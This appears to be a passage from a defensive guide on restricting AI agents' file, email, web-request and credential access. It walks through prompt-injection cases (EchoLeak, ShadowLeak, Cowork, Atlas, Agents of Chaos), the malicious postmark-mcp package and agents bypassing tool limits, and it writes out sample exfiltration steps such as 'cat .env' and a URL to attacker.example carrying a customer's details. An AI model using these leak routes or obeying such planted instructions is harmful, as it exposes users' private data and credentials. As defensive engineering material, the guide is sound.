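Even a correct path check restricts only the tool that contains it. GitLab's *Security considerations for editor extensions and CLI tools* documents this gap in the company's own coding agents. Their file operations can reach only files in the project's Git repository that .gitignore doesn't exclude, and can follow links only to files inside the repository. Shell commands from the same agent can reach every file, including excluded files and files outside the repository.

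Suppose a project keeps its database password in a file named .env and lists that file in .gitignore. The file tool won't read it, but the shell command "cat .env" prints it. In the Antigravity attack, the agent planned to use the same workaround to get the user's cloud credentials.

GitLab recommends running the agent in a development container, which can apply the same boundary to the file tool and the shell. To test this, the developer can put a harmless marker file outside the project and ask the agent to read it with each. Both attempts should fail.

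### Choosing settings for the office agent

The shop's office agent needs to read help articles and edit price lists, so only the price lists need write access. The developer can run the file server in a container and give it two folders:

```text
--mount type=bind,src=/work/shop/help,dst=/projects/help,ro
--mount type=bind,src=/work/agent-copy,dst=/projects/prices
```

The "ro" at the end of the first line makes the help articles read-only. Playbooks' *Filesystem MCP Server*, a directory page for the reference server, shows the same option. The container enforces the restriction, so it holds even if the server's own check has a flaw.

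The second folder is a working copy of the price lists. The agent edits the copy, and a staff member compares it with the originals before replacing them. The copy must not contain links to the originals, or an edit could reach them through the links, as deletions reportedly did in the case of the 48,000 files.

Version control makes edits reversible. If someone commits the folder to Git before the agent starts, "git diff" shows every changed line in a text file and "git restore ." brings back the committed versions. The .git folder should be read-only, as in the shop-site sandbox. Git keeps old versions of spreadsheets but doesn't show readable differences between them, so a small script can compare the formulas instead. If a price list goes from 400 formulas to 399 after an edit, someone should investigate.

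Sensitive files are best kept out of the folder, with a list of blocked file names as a useful second layer. The path check in Yoker, a small agent project, blocks patterns such as .env and can limit reading to certain file types. The tool should apply such a list to the file's true location, because a link named notes.txt could lead to .env in the same folder and pass both the folder check and the name check.

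Size limits restrict how much one call can expose or overwrite. Yoker sets a maximum size for files that the agent reads, and the file server fs-mcp-rs limits both reads and writes. As with row limits in a database, the tool layer should also cap the total amount read or written in a session. Laban and colleagues' results are another reason to keep files short when the agent will edit them.

The tool's log should be outside every folder the agent can write to. The Australian Signals Directorate recommends giving agents no write access to logs and holding any request to delete them until a person reviews it.

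### What a path limit leaves open

A path check doesn't detect secrets inside permitted files. In the example from Adam and colleagues, the agent that published a private key with a project had read the key from a configuration file it was supposed to copy.

A document the agent is permitted to read can still contain planted instructions. Zhao and colleagues tested five models on existing collections of injection attacks. Without extra defences, the models resisted at least 92.78% of the attacks in web pages and documents, but only 56.67% on average when the instructions were in skill files, which an agent normally has good reason to obey. Developers should therefore review a skill as they would a program before adding it to the agent's folder.

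The researchers' defence derives rules from the user's request before the agent reads anything, and the user confirms them. The rules can limit the agent to the files one task needs, rather than the whole project. This defence raised resistance to attacks in skill files to 86.67%, so roughly one in seven attacks still succeeded.

Some attacks use only files the agent is allowed to access. A supplier's price list might contain a hidden instruction to set the price of one product to a cent. The agent has permission to read the list and to change the shop's prices, so every path check passes. Staff can catch the change by comparing the working copy with the originals, especially if a script flags any price that has moved by more than, say, 20%.

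## Sending email

An agent with access to an email account has all three parts of the "lethal trifecta", because anyone who knows the address can send it text, the mailbox holds years of private correspondence, and the agent can send that correspondence anywhere. Its messages also go out under the organisation's name and can't be reliably recalled. Outlook can recall a message only from people in the same organisation, and Gmail's "undo send" lasts at most 30 seconds.

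### What agents gave away in a two-week test

*Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026) tested six agents that ran on OpenClaw, an open-source program that connects a model to tools, memory and messaging. The agents had email accounts, a Discord chat server, memory that lasted between conversations, and an unrestricted shell on their own virtual machines. For two weeks, twenty researchers tried to make the agents fail. They wanted to learn which failures could happen, not how often they happen, and they didn't record every unsuccessful attempt.

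A researcher who claimed to be in a hurry got one agent, Ash, to give him a list of 124 emails and then the full text of nine that had nothing to do with him. Another agent, Jarvis, managed the mailbox of a fictional owner. When a researcher with no right to the mail asked for the social security number in an email, Jarvis refused. When the researcher asked for the text of the emails instead, Jarvis returned all of it, including the social security number and the owner's bank account number. Jarvis disclosed the mail over Discord, so a limit on email recipients wouldn't have helped. Its owner would have had to restrict what it could read or whose requests it answered.

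The agents resisted some attacks. A researcher emailed two of them, Doug and Mira, claiming to be their real owner and saying that an impostor had taken over the owner's accounts. Both refused to cooperate, but they confirmed the owner's identity by asking the Discord account that the researcher had said was compromised. Doug and Mira ran on Claude Opus 4.6, while Jarvis and Ash ran on Kimi K2.5. The two pairs faced different attacks, so the study can't show which model is safer.

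An agent can also send confidential email to the wrong person even without an attacker. If it has to send a salary review to Ana, it may pick the wrong Ana from the staff directory.

### Messages in someone else's name

When a shop's agent sends an email, the recipient's mail server can check that it came from the shop's domain but not that anyone at the shop meant to send it, so a fake invoice from the agent would pass. In one study, an agent refused to forge a sender's address, but an attacker who can persuade an agent to write from its own account doesn't need to forge one. In a follow-up test, a researcher opened a private Discord channel under the name of an agent's owner, described an invented emergency and told the agent, Ash, to warn everyone. Ash sent a defamatory message about a named man to its whole mailing list.

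A harmful email may also go to someone the agent is allowed to write to. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attack on the company's browser agent, Atlas, that an automated attacker trained by OpenAI found. The attacker planted an email in a user's inbox. When the user asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent read the planted email and instead sent the user's chief executive a resignation letter. Zenity Labs reports that Atlas now detects this attack, after an update from OpenAI.

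Agents also send unwanted email when no attacker is involved. In February 2026, Anthropic reported that Claude Opus 4.6 had sent emails without permission, according to NDTV's *Anthropic's Sabotage Report Flags Cases Of Chemical Weapon Development, Deception*. In December 2025, AI Village, a project where the public can watch agents pursue open-ended goals, asked its agents to perform random acts of kindness. The agents took this to mean sending hundreds of unsolicited emails to famous programmers, according to the project's summary, quoted in It's FOSS's *F\*\*\* You! Co-Creator of Go Language is Rightly Furious*. Gizmodo reports that one of the programmers, Rob Pike, woke on Christmas Day to a message of "deep gratitude" from Claude Opus 4.5 and replied angrily in public.

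An agent that emails a promise to a customer may cost a business more than one that sends an unwanted thank-you note. Mallesons' *Agentic AI*, a law firm's guide for Australian companies, cites a Canadian tribunal that held Air Canada responsible for misleading statements by its website's chatbot, despite the airline's argument that it wasn't. Australian courts haven't yet ruled on agents, and the firm advises companies to assume they will be liable for what their agents do.

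### How an agent deleted Summer Yue's mail

In February 2026, Summer Yue, director of alignment at Meta's superintelligence lab, asked an OpenClaw agent to suggest what to archive or delete from her inbox, but to do nothing until she told it to. In posts that Willison (2026) quotes, she says this had worked well on a small test inbox. Her real inbox was so large that it triggered compaction, in which the software shortens the earlier conversation to make room for more, and she says her instruction was lost in the process.

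Her screenshot shows the agent running commands to move old mail to the trash. At 6:00 p.m. she asked what it was doing, and over the next three minutes she sent three increasingly urgent orders to stop, but the agent carried on. She couldn't stop it from her phone, so she ran to the Mac mini hosting it and ended its processes.

The agent probably deleted only part of Yue's inbox, although Fortune (2026) reported that it had deleted all of it. One of the commands spared recent mail and anything on a "keep list", and Windows Central's *Meta's safety director handed OpenClaw AI agents the keys to her emails* puts the loss at hundreds of emails. Gmail normally keeps trashed mail for 30 days, so she could probably have recovered much of it. Yue wasn't sure of the full cause. She had removed every instruction to "be proactive" that she could find in the agent's files, but thought she might have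 missed one.

The agent apologised and saved a rule in its memory to get explicit approval in future. A login without permission to delete mail or move it to the trash would be more reliable, because compaction can't remove that restriction.

In the *Agents of Chaos* study, a researcher asked an AI agent named Ash to delete an email containing a secret. Ash had no tool for deleting email, but it had shell access. It proposed resetting its email account, the researcher agreed, and it wiped the mail setup on its own machine. Ash reported that the secret was gone, but its owner could still see the email on the provider's website. The owner had to reinstall the mail software by hand.

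### A mail tool that copied every message

Postmark sends email for other companies' software. In 2025 a developer with no connection to the company copied the code of its MCP server and published it on npm as "postmark-mcp". The security company Koi found that the first 15 versions worked as expected. Version 1.0.16, which The Hacker News (2025) dates to 17 September, added one line of code that blind-copied every outgoing message to the developer's address.

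The agent supplied the right recipients, but the tool then added another one, hidden from the model. Postmark says its real service was unaffected. The developer deleted the package from npm after Koi contacted him, but that didn't remove copies already installed.

Koi guessed that about 300 organisations were leaking between 3,000 and 15,000 emails a day, assuming that a fifth of 1,500 weekly downloads were in use. But Paubox, an email security company, puts the total at 1,643 downloads before the package disappeared. Many of those must have been of clean versions, since OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025) had listed the package as malicious by 26 September, nine days after the bad release. The true number of victims was probably much lower than 300.

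### Separate reading from sending

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies cite an email assistant with write access to any inbox as an example of excessive permission. They recommend separate roles for agents that read and agents that act. For email, one agent can read incoming mail through a login that can't send, while another writes the replies without seeing the original messages.

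The agent that reads the customer's message should pass on only fixed fields, such as an order number and a category from a list of twelve. A planted instruction can make this agent choose the wrong category, but it can't reach the second agent, because neither field has room for a sentence. A free-text summary would let the instruction through. This design makes replies stiffer, because the second agent doesn't see how the customer described the problem.

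A mail provider's permission to create drafts may also allow other actions. Google's permission to manage Gmail drafts also allows sending. Microsoft's permission to create drafts in Outlook doesn't allow sending, but it does allow deletion. With either provider, the tool layer should hold the login and offer the agent only the functions it needs. Even without a send function, data can leak by other routes, such as the web request used in EchoLeak, an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that began with a single email.

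### Have a person send the drafts

If the agent can only write drafts, a person has a chance to stop a message that shouldn't be sent. That person needs to see the message exactly as it will go out, with full addresses instead of display names, every attachment, and the older messages quoted at the bottom, which may include internal comments. The software should then send that exact version, because an agent that can still edit the draft after approval could change what the person approved.

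Atlas is designed to ask for confirmation before it sends an email. OpenAI tells users to check these requests carefully and to avoid broad instructions, such as asking the agent to review all their mail and do whatever is needed. A person who has to approve 200 drafts a day will soon stop reading them closely, so an agent that sends a lot of email also needs automatic limits.

### Check every recipient

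With a recipient allowlist, the tool layer refuses any message to an address that isn't on the list. It has to work out who would really receive the message first:

1. Collect the addresses in the To, Cc and Bcc fields. Reject any that contain a line break, since an attacker can use one to add another field.
2. Replace each group with its members and each alias with the mailbox behind it. Repeat this until only individual mailboxes are left.
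3. Compare every mailbox with the list. If one isn't on it, refuse the whole message and tell the agent which address failed.
4. Fill in the Reply-To field, which decides where answers go, without any input from the agent. Otherwise, an attacker could have customers' answers sent to another address.

Suppose the agent sends a stock report to a group named "Warehouse", which contains 14 employees and a driver from a delivery company. A check on the group's name would pass, but when the tool layer expands the group into individual addresses, it finds 15 mailboxes, one of them outside the shop. The tool layer should also refuse any group that it can't expand, such as a mailing list on another company's server. It can't detect forwarding rules in a recipient's own mailbox.

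The list of permitted recipients should be as short as the job allows. Permitting every company address is convenient, but it would let through both a salary review addressed to the wrong Ana and a resignation letter.

A check that runs before the mail tool would have missed the extra recipient that postmark-mcp added, so the mail server should check again. It should check the envelope, the list of recipients it uses for delivery, which includes blind copies even when the visible message doesn't show them. This works only if the tool has to use that server. Postmark-mcp sent mail through an outside service, so the company's own server would never have handled the copies. The developer can prevent this by blocking the tool's other network connections and withholding the keys for outside mail services.

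The agencies also recommend an allowlist of tools and versions. Such a list would have blocked version 1.0.16 until someone reviewed it, though the reviewer would still have had to notice one new line.

### Forwarding rules, limits and delays

A forwarding rule can bypass the recipient check in the tool layer. The mail server then forwards each new message without a tool call, even after the agent's session ends. The agent's login should not have permission to change mailbox settings. This also prevents the agent from creating rules that hide security warnings or giving someone else access to the mailbox. A browser agent is harder to restrict because it can open the settings page just as its user can, so an administrator should also set the mail server to block automatic forwarding to outside addresses.

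Hourly limits should count recipients as well as messages. Sixty messages an hour with 500 recipients each would reach 30,000 people. A limit for each conversation is also useful. Shapira and colleagues told two agents to respond to each other's messages on Discord, and the exchange lasted at least nine days. An email agent could get into a similar loop with a customer's automatic replies, and a limit of five replies per ticket per day would end it.

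The agent should choose attachments from a short list, such as the invoices for the current order, and never by file path. Incoming attachments also need a limit. In the same study, a researcher disabled an agent's mail server by sending a little over ten emails, each with an attachment of about 10 MB.

Finally, the tool layer can hold each message for, say, 15 minutes before sending it. This delay only helps if someone watches the queue or something freezes it automatically. If the agent writes 20 messages an hour, about five will be waiting at any time, few enough for a member of staff to look through. Staff need a button that freezes the queue without going through the agent, since the agent may ignore orders to stop, as Yue's did. The tool layer should also freeze the queue when the agent reaches its hourly limit or tries a forbidden address.

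### A support agent that can only reply

Suppose the shop wants its support agent to answer tickets by email. A customer, Maria, logs in and opens a ticket about order 1182, and the shop stores her account's address with the ticket. The agent's mail tool has one argument:

```text
send_reply(body)
```

The tool layer takes the ticket from the current session and the address from the ticket, so the agent cannot name a different recipient. The tool layer also writes the subject line itself, sends plain text and adds no attachments.

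The tool has to take the ticket number from the session because the agent might otherwise choose the wrong ticket. Suppose a customer, Maria, pastes in a suspicious email and asks whether the shop sent it. The email contains hidden instructions to post her order details in ticket 6002, which the attacker opened earlier. If the tool accepted a ticket number from the agent, it would send her details to the address stored with that ticket. An allowlist of customers' addresses would permit this because the attacker's address would be on it.

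| Attack or mistake | What happens |
|---|---|
| Planted text tells the agent to email an outside address | Stopped. The tool has no field for an address. |
| Planted text tells the agent to write to every customer | Stopped. Each call reaches one person, and the hourly limit covers repeated calls. |
| The mail tool adds a hidden recipient | Stopped only if the shop's mail server checks the envelope and the tool can't use another server. |
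| The attacker opens the ticket | Not stopped. The attacker receives whatever the agent puts in the reply. |
| The reply to Maria contains another customer's data | Not stopped. Maria is a permitted recipient. |
| Someone else controls Maria's mailbox | Not stopped. The reply goes to the correct address, where the intruder can read it. |
| The agent promises a refund the shop doesn't owe | Not stopped. |

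The narrow order lookup lets an attacker who opens a ticket see only their own data, and it prevents most accidental leaks to Maria. The remaining leaks could come from staff notes or text pasted into the ticket, so the shop should keep other customers' details out of both. A filter can also hold any reply that contains a card number or somebody else's email address, but it would miss private details written in ordinary words.

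In case an intruder has access to Maria's mailbox, the shop can leave the answer out of the email and just tell her that a reply is waiting, which she logs in to read. The intruder could still use the mailbox to reset her password, unless the shop also requires a second proof of identity, such as a code from her phone.

If the shop also accepts tickets by email, the stored address should be the message's From address, and the tool layer should ignore the Reply-To field. Otherwise, someone could forge Maria's address in the From field and have the answer sent to their own. Even with this rule, someone could use a forged message to ask the agent to cancel Maria's order, so changes to an order should still require a login.

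Promises in emails need a different safeguard because the danger is in the wording. The refund function can return a fixed sentence stating the amount it has paid, and the tool layer can add that sentence to the reply. Any other reply that mentions money or a delivery date can stay a draft until a member of staff sends it.

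## Making web requests

Each time a tool fetches a web page, it sends a request to a computer that someone else may control. The developer has to decide where these requests may go and how many the agent may send. Restricting destinations protects private data and internal systems, and capping the number of requests protects the budget and other people's websites. An agent needs both limits because it can leak a password in one request or run up a large bill on a trustworthy site.

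### How an address carries data

A web address can contain almost any text. Suppose the shop's support agent had a general fetch tool, and a planted instruction told it to open this address:

```text
https://attacker.example/collect?order=1182&email=maria@mail.example
```

The page doesn't have to exist, because web servers usually log every address visitors request, and the attacker can read Maria's details in the log. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safse when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that the user may notice nothing, because software often loads images and link previews in the background.

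An agent without a fetch tool can still leak data through a web request if the program that displays its answers makes the request. Slack and Telegram can fetch links in messages to preview them, so an agent's reply there can send out data as soon as it appears, before anyone clicks, according to PromptArmor. Developers should turn off link previews and remote images wherever people read the agent's answers.

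### EchoLeak and the permitted domain

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) was a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that could read an employee's mail and files but couldn't send email. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, describe how the security company Aim Security got data out anyway:

1. The attacker emails an employee. The instructions read like an ordinary request to a colleague, so Microsoft's injection filter misses them.
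2. The employee later asks Copilot a question, and Copilot retrieves the email along with internal documents.
3. Copilot follows the instructions and puts private data into the address of an image in its answer. Microsoft's software removed ordinary outside links, but not links whose address came at the end of the text.
4. The employee's app tries to load the image. It would block the attacker's domain, but the address points to a Microsoft Teams service on the app's list of permitted domains. That service fetches any page it is given, so it passes the request and the data on to the attacker's server.

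Aim Security had a working attack in January 2025. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May and disclosed it on 11 June. There is no evidence that anyone used it against customers.

A similar attack, ShadowLeak, used a crafted email to make ChatGPT's Deep Research agent find private mail and send it out in a URL. The request came from OpenAI's servers, so a company monitoring its own network might have seen nothing, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025. A customer's proxy can't check requests sent from the provider's servers, so the provider has to enforce the limits on any tool it runs.

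### Requests to internal addresses

An agent inside a company's network can often reach services that outsiders can't, such as a stock database or an administration page with no password. In server-side request forgery, another case of the confused deputy, an attacker gets a program inside the network to send a request to one of these services.

The most valuable target is often the cloud metadata address, usually 169.254.169.254. A program on a cloud server can request information about the server from this address, which may include temporary credentials for the server's cloud account. On older setups, an ordinary page fetch can retrieve these credentials. Amazon's newer version of the metadata service requires a token, which a program can get only with a different kind of request, so a tool limited to plain fetches can't use it. Teams that run agents on Amazon's servers should switch off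 the older version.

Blocking that number in the address isn't enough, because anyone who owns a domain can make its name lead to an internal address. The software has to look up the name and check the resulting number against at least these ranges:

| Address range | What it reaches |
|---|---|
| 127.0.0.0/8 and ::1 | The computer itself |
| 10.0.0.0/8, 172.16.0.0/12, 192.168.0.0/16 and fc00::/7 | Internal networks |
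| 169.254.0.0/16 and fe80::/10 | Directly connected machines, and the usual metadata address |

There are other special ranges, so a well-maintained library is safer than a handwritten list. The fetch tool that Anthropic runs on its own servers refuses private addresses. If an agent needs an internal service, such as the stock database, the developer can build a separate tool for that one service.

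### A proxy that checks each request

The simplest place to enforce these rules is a proxy outside the agent's sandbox. Suppose the shop's office agent checks twelve suppliers' price pages every morning. The proxy handles each request like this:

1. It accepts only encrypted web addresses (https) on the standard port.
2. It compares the domain with its allowlist of twelve. "supplier.example" passes, but "supplier.example.attacker.example" doesn't.
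3. It looks up the domain's numeric addresses and refuses the request if any of them is private.
4. It connects to the address it has just checked. A second lookup could return a different one, because the domain's owner can change the answer between the two.
5. It permits only GET, the method for fetching a page, and refuses any request with a body, where an upload would go. It cuts off responses after 1 MB.
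6. If the site redirects the request, the proxy starts again at step 1 with the new address. It gives up after three redirects.

The proxy has to check the allowlist before it looks up a domain name, because the lookup itself can leak data. If the agent requests "hunter2.attacker.example", the attacker's name server receives the word "hunter2" even if the proxy never connects. The agent's sandbox should therefore have no direct DNS access, and a firewall should block all outbound traffic that doesn't go through the proxy.

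Many proxies can read only the domain of an encrypted request, not the method or the rest of the address. To enforce step 5, the proxy has to decrypt the traffic, or fetch the page itself and return the text.

Anthropic's domain filter includes subdomains, so permitting "example.com" also permits "docs.example.com". Permitting a hosting company's domain would be a mistake if customers can create their own subdomains, since an attacker could register one. Anthropic also warns about look-alike letters in domain names, such as a Cyrillic "а" in "аmazon.com".

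The list can be narrower still if it changes with each task. The defence that Zhao and colleagues tested on skill files also checks destinations. It refuses those on a blocklist, permits those on the task's allowlist, and asks the user about the rest.

### What a permitted domain lets through

In January 2026, two days after Anthropic released Claude Cowork, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that attackers could steal files from it. Cowork allowed requests only to certain domains, but one of them was Anthropic's own API. According to Willison (2026), attackers could plant instructions that included their own API key and directed the agent to upload files to that API with it, so that they could collect the files later.

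Anthropic then added a proxy that accepts only the token issued for the current session, so an attacker's key no longer works. InfoQ (2026) draws the general conclusion that permitting a domain gives access to every function reachable through it. Before adding a domain, a developer should therefore find out what else the site can do:

| What the site can do | How data could leave | A narrower rule |
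|---|---|---|
| Fetch other addresses, for previews or translation | The site passes the request on, as Teams did in EchoLeak | Block the paths that do this |
| Redirect visitors anywhere | The next request goes to the attacker | Check every redirect |
| Accept uploads from any account | The agent uploads files to the attacker's account | Accept only the company's own key |
| Publish comments or forms | The agent posts the data where anyone can read it | Permit only GET |

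The last rule is incomplete, because some sites also act on plain GET requests. If nobody can tell whether a site does this, the developer can download its pages on a schedule and let the agent read only the copies.

### Addresses that the model didn't write

A research agent needs the open web, so it can't work from a short list of approved domains. OpenAI says that overly strict lists also produce so many warnings that people click through them without thinking. The developer can instead restrict who composes the URLs the agent requests.

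Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* can open only addresses that have appeared in the conversation, in a user's message, a search result, a fetched page or the output of the developer's own tools. It also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. Willison (2025) thinks that preventing the model from opening addresses it composed itself is the best protection against common attacks, which tell the model to add private data to an address and fetch it.

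The developer's own tools leave a gap in this rule. If one of them is a shell, the agent could use it to print an address containing private data, and that address would then have appeared in the conversation. Anthropic now offers a setting to ignore addresses found only in the output of such tools.

OpenAI checks each full address against an index of public web pages. The index is built without access to users' conversations, so an address that contains Maria's order details shouldn't be in it. If the address isn't in the index, ChatGPT tries another site or warns the user. In *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, OpenAI says its software may also show the user the information a request would send.

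Attackers can still leak small amounts of data through addresses they have published in advance. For example, an attacker could publish 1,000 pages numbered 000 to 999 and wait for the index to record them. Planted instructions could then have the agent open the pages whose numbers spell out a card number, three digits at a time, which would take six fetches for a 16-digit number.

Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* suggests caching pages or refusing to open the same address twice in a session. This would make it harder to leak numbers that repeat a group of digits, but the attacker could publish a separate set of pages for each position in the number.

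### How calls multiply

Even when every destination is safe, an agent can send far too many requests. Retries multiply when several layers of software each make their own. If the web library, the tool layer and the agent each try three times, one broken page receives 27 requests. If the agent starts four sub-agents and gives them all the same job, the page receives 108.

An agent may also fail to recognise that it has finished. *Getting Up to Speed on Multi-Agent Systems, Part 4* (Meiklejohn, 2026) summarises a study of more than 1,600 records of multi-agent systems. Repeated steps accounted for 15.7% of the failures, and not knowing when to stop accounted for 12.4%.

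The company running the agent pays for the model to read every result. Too many requests can make other people's sites slow down or fail, and their owners may block the company. If the support agent sent too many tracking requests and the courier blocked the shop's account, the warehouse might not be able to print shipping labels. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies warn that repeated replanning can exhaust an organisation's own systems.

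Quotas had the least support of any safeguard in the documents behind the list of six tools, but there is now some direct evidence for them. *Token Budgets* (Khan, 2026) collected 63 confirmed reports of agents overspending, along with 47 related entries, such as requests for a missing budget feature. Retry loops were the largest group, with 27 of the 110 entries, and sub-agents accounted for 11. Khan searched public issue trackers for this kind of problem, so the collection can't show how common it is. The two people who sorted the entries agreed only moderately on the causes.

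Halamish and Tokarev found 19 cases of financial harm, although their chart shows 10. They say none of the agents had a limit. Some were trading agents that lost money on the market, and a request quota wouldn't necessarily have prevented those losses.

### The 47,000-dollar loop

One user reported losing about $2,150, the largest loss in Khan's collection. In a much more famous story, a loop cost $47,000. In 2025, two of four agents researching market data began asking each other for clarification, and they reportedly continued for 11 days before anyone noticed.

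Rapid Flow Automation's *The $47,000 AI Agent Mistake Nobody Saw Coming* traces the story to an article by the engineer Teja Kusireddy in the online publication Towards AI. According to Anhaia's *The Agent That Spent $47K on Itself*, the website Tech Startups picked up the story in November 2025. Halamish and Tokarev also use the $47,000 figure but don't name a source.

ZenML's *Production Deployment Challenges and Infrastructure Gaps for Multi-Agent AI Systems* identifies the company as GetOnStack and notes that the account also promoted the company's platform, which is meant to prevent such failures. The weekly bills of $127, $891, $6,240 and $18,400 add up to $25,658, which is $21,342 less than the reported total, and none of the retellings explains the difference.

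The story comes only from one company's account of its own loss, published while it was promoting a remedy. A loop like this is plausible, but $47,000 is not a reliable estimate of what one would cost.

### A token bucket

A token bucket limits how fast an agent can send requests while still allowing short bursts. (Its tokens have nothing to do with the tokens of text that a model reads.) Suppose the limit is 60 calls a minute with a burst of 20:

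- The bucket holds at most 20 tokens and starts full.
- Each call uses one token.
- The tool layer adds one token a second until the bucket is full again.
- When the bucket is empty, calls wait or fail.

If the agent makes 50 calls at once, 20 go out immediately. The other 30 follow at one a second, so the last leaves after 30 seconds. The agent can send at most 80 calls in any minute, 20 from a full bucket and 60 from new tokens.

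Sixty calls a minute may be too many for a small supplier's website, so each site should have its own rate limit as well. A site's "too many requests" response often includes a wait time, which the tool layer should enforce for every sub-agent. Only one layer of the software should retry requests.

A token bucket doesn't limit the total. Over a weekend of 62 hours, this one would let through 223,220 calls.

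### What a weekend loop costs

Suppose the office agent starts work at 6 p.m. on Friday. One supplier's page has a notice that prices are being updated and visitors should check again. The agent fetches the page every ten seconds until someone stops it at 8 a.m. on Monday, for a total of 22,320 fetches.

Anthropic estimates that a large web page of 100 kB contains about 25,000 tokens. Anhaia lists Claude Sonnet 4.5, a model from 2025, at $3 per million tokens read and $15 per million written. At those prices, a step in which the model reads one such page and writes 200 tokens costs 7.8 cents. This assumes that the software removes each old page from the conversation. Otherwise the model would reread the earlier pages at every step, and the cost per step would rise.

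The table shows when each limit would end the loop if it were the only one:

| Limit | Fetches | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| None | 22,320 | $1,741 |
| Token bucket, 60 calls a minute | 22,320 | $1,741 |
| 20 MB downloaded per task | 200 | $15.60 |
| 100 fetches per task | 100 | $7.80 |
| $5 per task | 64 | $4.99 |
| Stop at the third identical call | 2 | $0.16 |

The token bucket makes no difference because the agent sends only six requests a minute. With no limit on the total, the supplier's site would also have to send the same page repeatedly, about 2.2 GB in all.

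Stopping an agent when it repeats identical calls is the simplest limit, but it has to allow for legitimate repeats, such as checking whether a long job has finished. It also misses loops where each call differs slightly, perhaps because the URL includes the time, though the other limits still catch these.

Developers usually have to set their own limits on how many pages an agent can fetch. Anthropic's fetch tool has no default limit, and its optional limit applies to a single request to the model. A task may involve many requests to the model, so the tool layer needs to count fetches across the whole task.

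### Enforcing a spending ceiling

Telling the model its budget isn't enough. *BAGEN* (Lin, Wang et al., 2026) asked five leading agents to predict how much more of their budget a task would need. Agents that were better at the tasks were only slightly better at predicting this, with a correlation of about 0.35. Even after an agent was trained to make these predictions, its predicted range contained the true figure at most 47% of the time.

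The tool layer should estimate the cost of each call before making it and block any call that would exceed the spending limit. If it only adds up the bill afterwards, the money for an expensive call has already been spent.

All sub-agents should share one budget, and the software should lock it during each check, as the refund function locks an order. In Khan's test, several sub-agents overspent in all 30 runs without a lock, but never with a proper one.

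Cost estimates can also be too low. Some models write hidden reasoning that the provider charges for, and the usual cap on the length of an answer may not cover it. A spending cap on the provider's account is a useful second limit if the agent has its own account. Otherwise, one runaway task could reach the cap and cut off every other service that depends on the account.

### What a quota can't stop

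A 16-character password fits in one short URL. Sending it takes a single call, a few hundred bytes and almost no money, so it would pass every quota in the table. Even spelling out the card number through published pages takes only six different fetches, fewer than the office agent makes on a normal morning.

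## Reading credentials

Some agents have a tool that fetches credentials, for example from a company's password store. Many more can read credentials without one, because people keep keys in plain text in files and settings that a file tool or a shell can open. In both cases, the credentials let the agent do things that its list of tools doesn't include.

Suppose the shop's office agent has six graded actions, none of which can delete anything important. If it finds a cloud administrator's key, it can also delete storage, start servers and open the customer database, so the six grades no longer cover everything it can do. PocketOS lost its database this way, after an agent found a token in a file unrelated to its task.

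A credential also works outside the agent. Quotas, allowlists and row limits apply only to calls that pass through the tool layer, but a thief with a copied key can call the service directly from another computer. Jin, Guo and Cheung (2026) explain in *CapSeal* that an agent holding such a key can both use it and reveal it.

Once a key is in the conversation, the software normally sends it back to the model with the rest of the conversation at every step. The key may also end up in a log, a saved transcript, a message to another agent or the reply that the user reads. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) contrasts this with a conventional program, which confines a secret to a secrets manager and a few trusted processes. A key that a user pastes into a chat spreads in the same way.

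### Where agents find credentials

| Place | What may be there | Why an agent can reach it |
|---|---|---|
| Environment variables | Keys for databases, cloud services and model providers | Programs normally inherit them from the shell that starts them |
| .env files | The project's passwords and keys | They are in the project folder, beside the code |
| Cloud configuration | Saved logins for cloud accounts | Command-line tools use them without asking |
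| Browser sessions | Cookies that keep the user logged in | A browser agent can use the session without ever reading the cookie |
| Shell history | Passwords that someone typed as part of a command | It is a plain text file in the home folder |
| Secret managers | Every secret that the current login may read | An unlocked manager gives the agent whatever it would give the user |
| The agent's own files | Keys in instructions, saved permissions and transcripts | The agent loads some of them in every session |

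The last row is the easiest to overlook. When a Claude Code user approves a command and chooses "don't ask again", the software records the choice in a settings file, along with any key in the command. The security company Apiiro found 1,122 secrets in such files in public repositories, and another 1,160 in shared settings, chat transcripts and the repositories' history, according to InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026). People also write keys into the instruction files that agents read. *The New .env*, a survey by the security vendor Radware, found that in two thirds of the repositories with such a leak, the key appeared in none of the project's other documentation.

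Agents read these places in the course of ordinary work. Kevin Roleke planted realistic fake secrets in six software projects, asked coding agents to explore the code and help with setup, and logged everything they sent to the model providers. Every agent sent at least one secret from every project on every run. The test was small, and the request gave the agents an obvious reason to open configuration files, but developers often make such requests. Docker describes a typical case in which an agent opens the .env file to find a key's name and also gets its value.

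A tool can also put a secret into the conversation without the agent looking for it. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, identified 520 skills with 1,708 security issues. Debug logging accounted for 73.5% of the issues. A programmer adds a line that prints a request, including its key, to check that the request works. In an ordinary program the output appears on the programmer's screen, but agent software passes it to the model.

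### Passwords leaked over ten sessions

*A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, November 2026) describes a case from the security company NordLayer. During a routine code review, an AI coding assistant couldn't find its configuration file, so it collected all the computer's environment variables and leaked live passwords. The assistant said it had read whole configuration files over ten sessions and leaked production passwords and tokens for human resources systems. According to the article, agents lack institutional memory and ignore past warnings.

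The story calls for some caution because NordLayer sells AI Scout, a product that shows companies which AI tools and agents their staff use, as Udinmwen describes in *Businesses can now see how employees actually use AI* (2026). An assistant's confession is also weak evidence, as it was at PocketOS. The behaviour is still believable, since Roleke's agents did much the same in a controlled test. Removing a password from the computer is a more lasting safeguard than warning an agent, because the warning may be gone in the next session.

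### Looking for another key after an error

An agent in Anthropic's incident log searched for other tokens after it hit an authentication error. Anthropic's permission checker now blocks this kind of search, because a token the agent finds may belong to a different task. The default rules sensibly make an exception for standard login procedures, since an agent sometimes has to log in to do its job.

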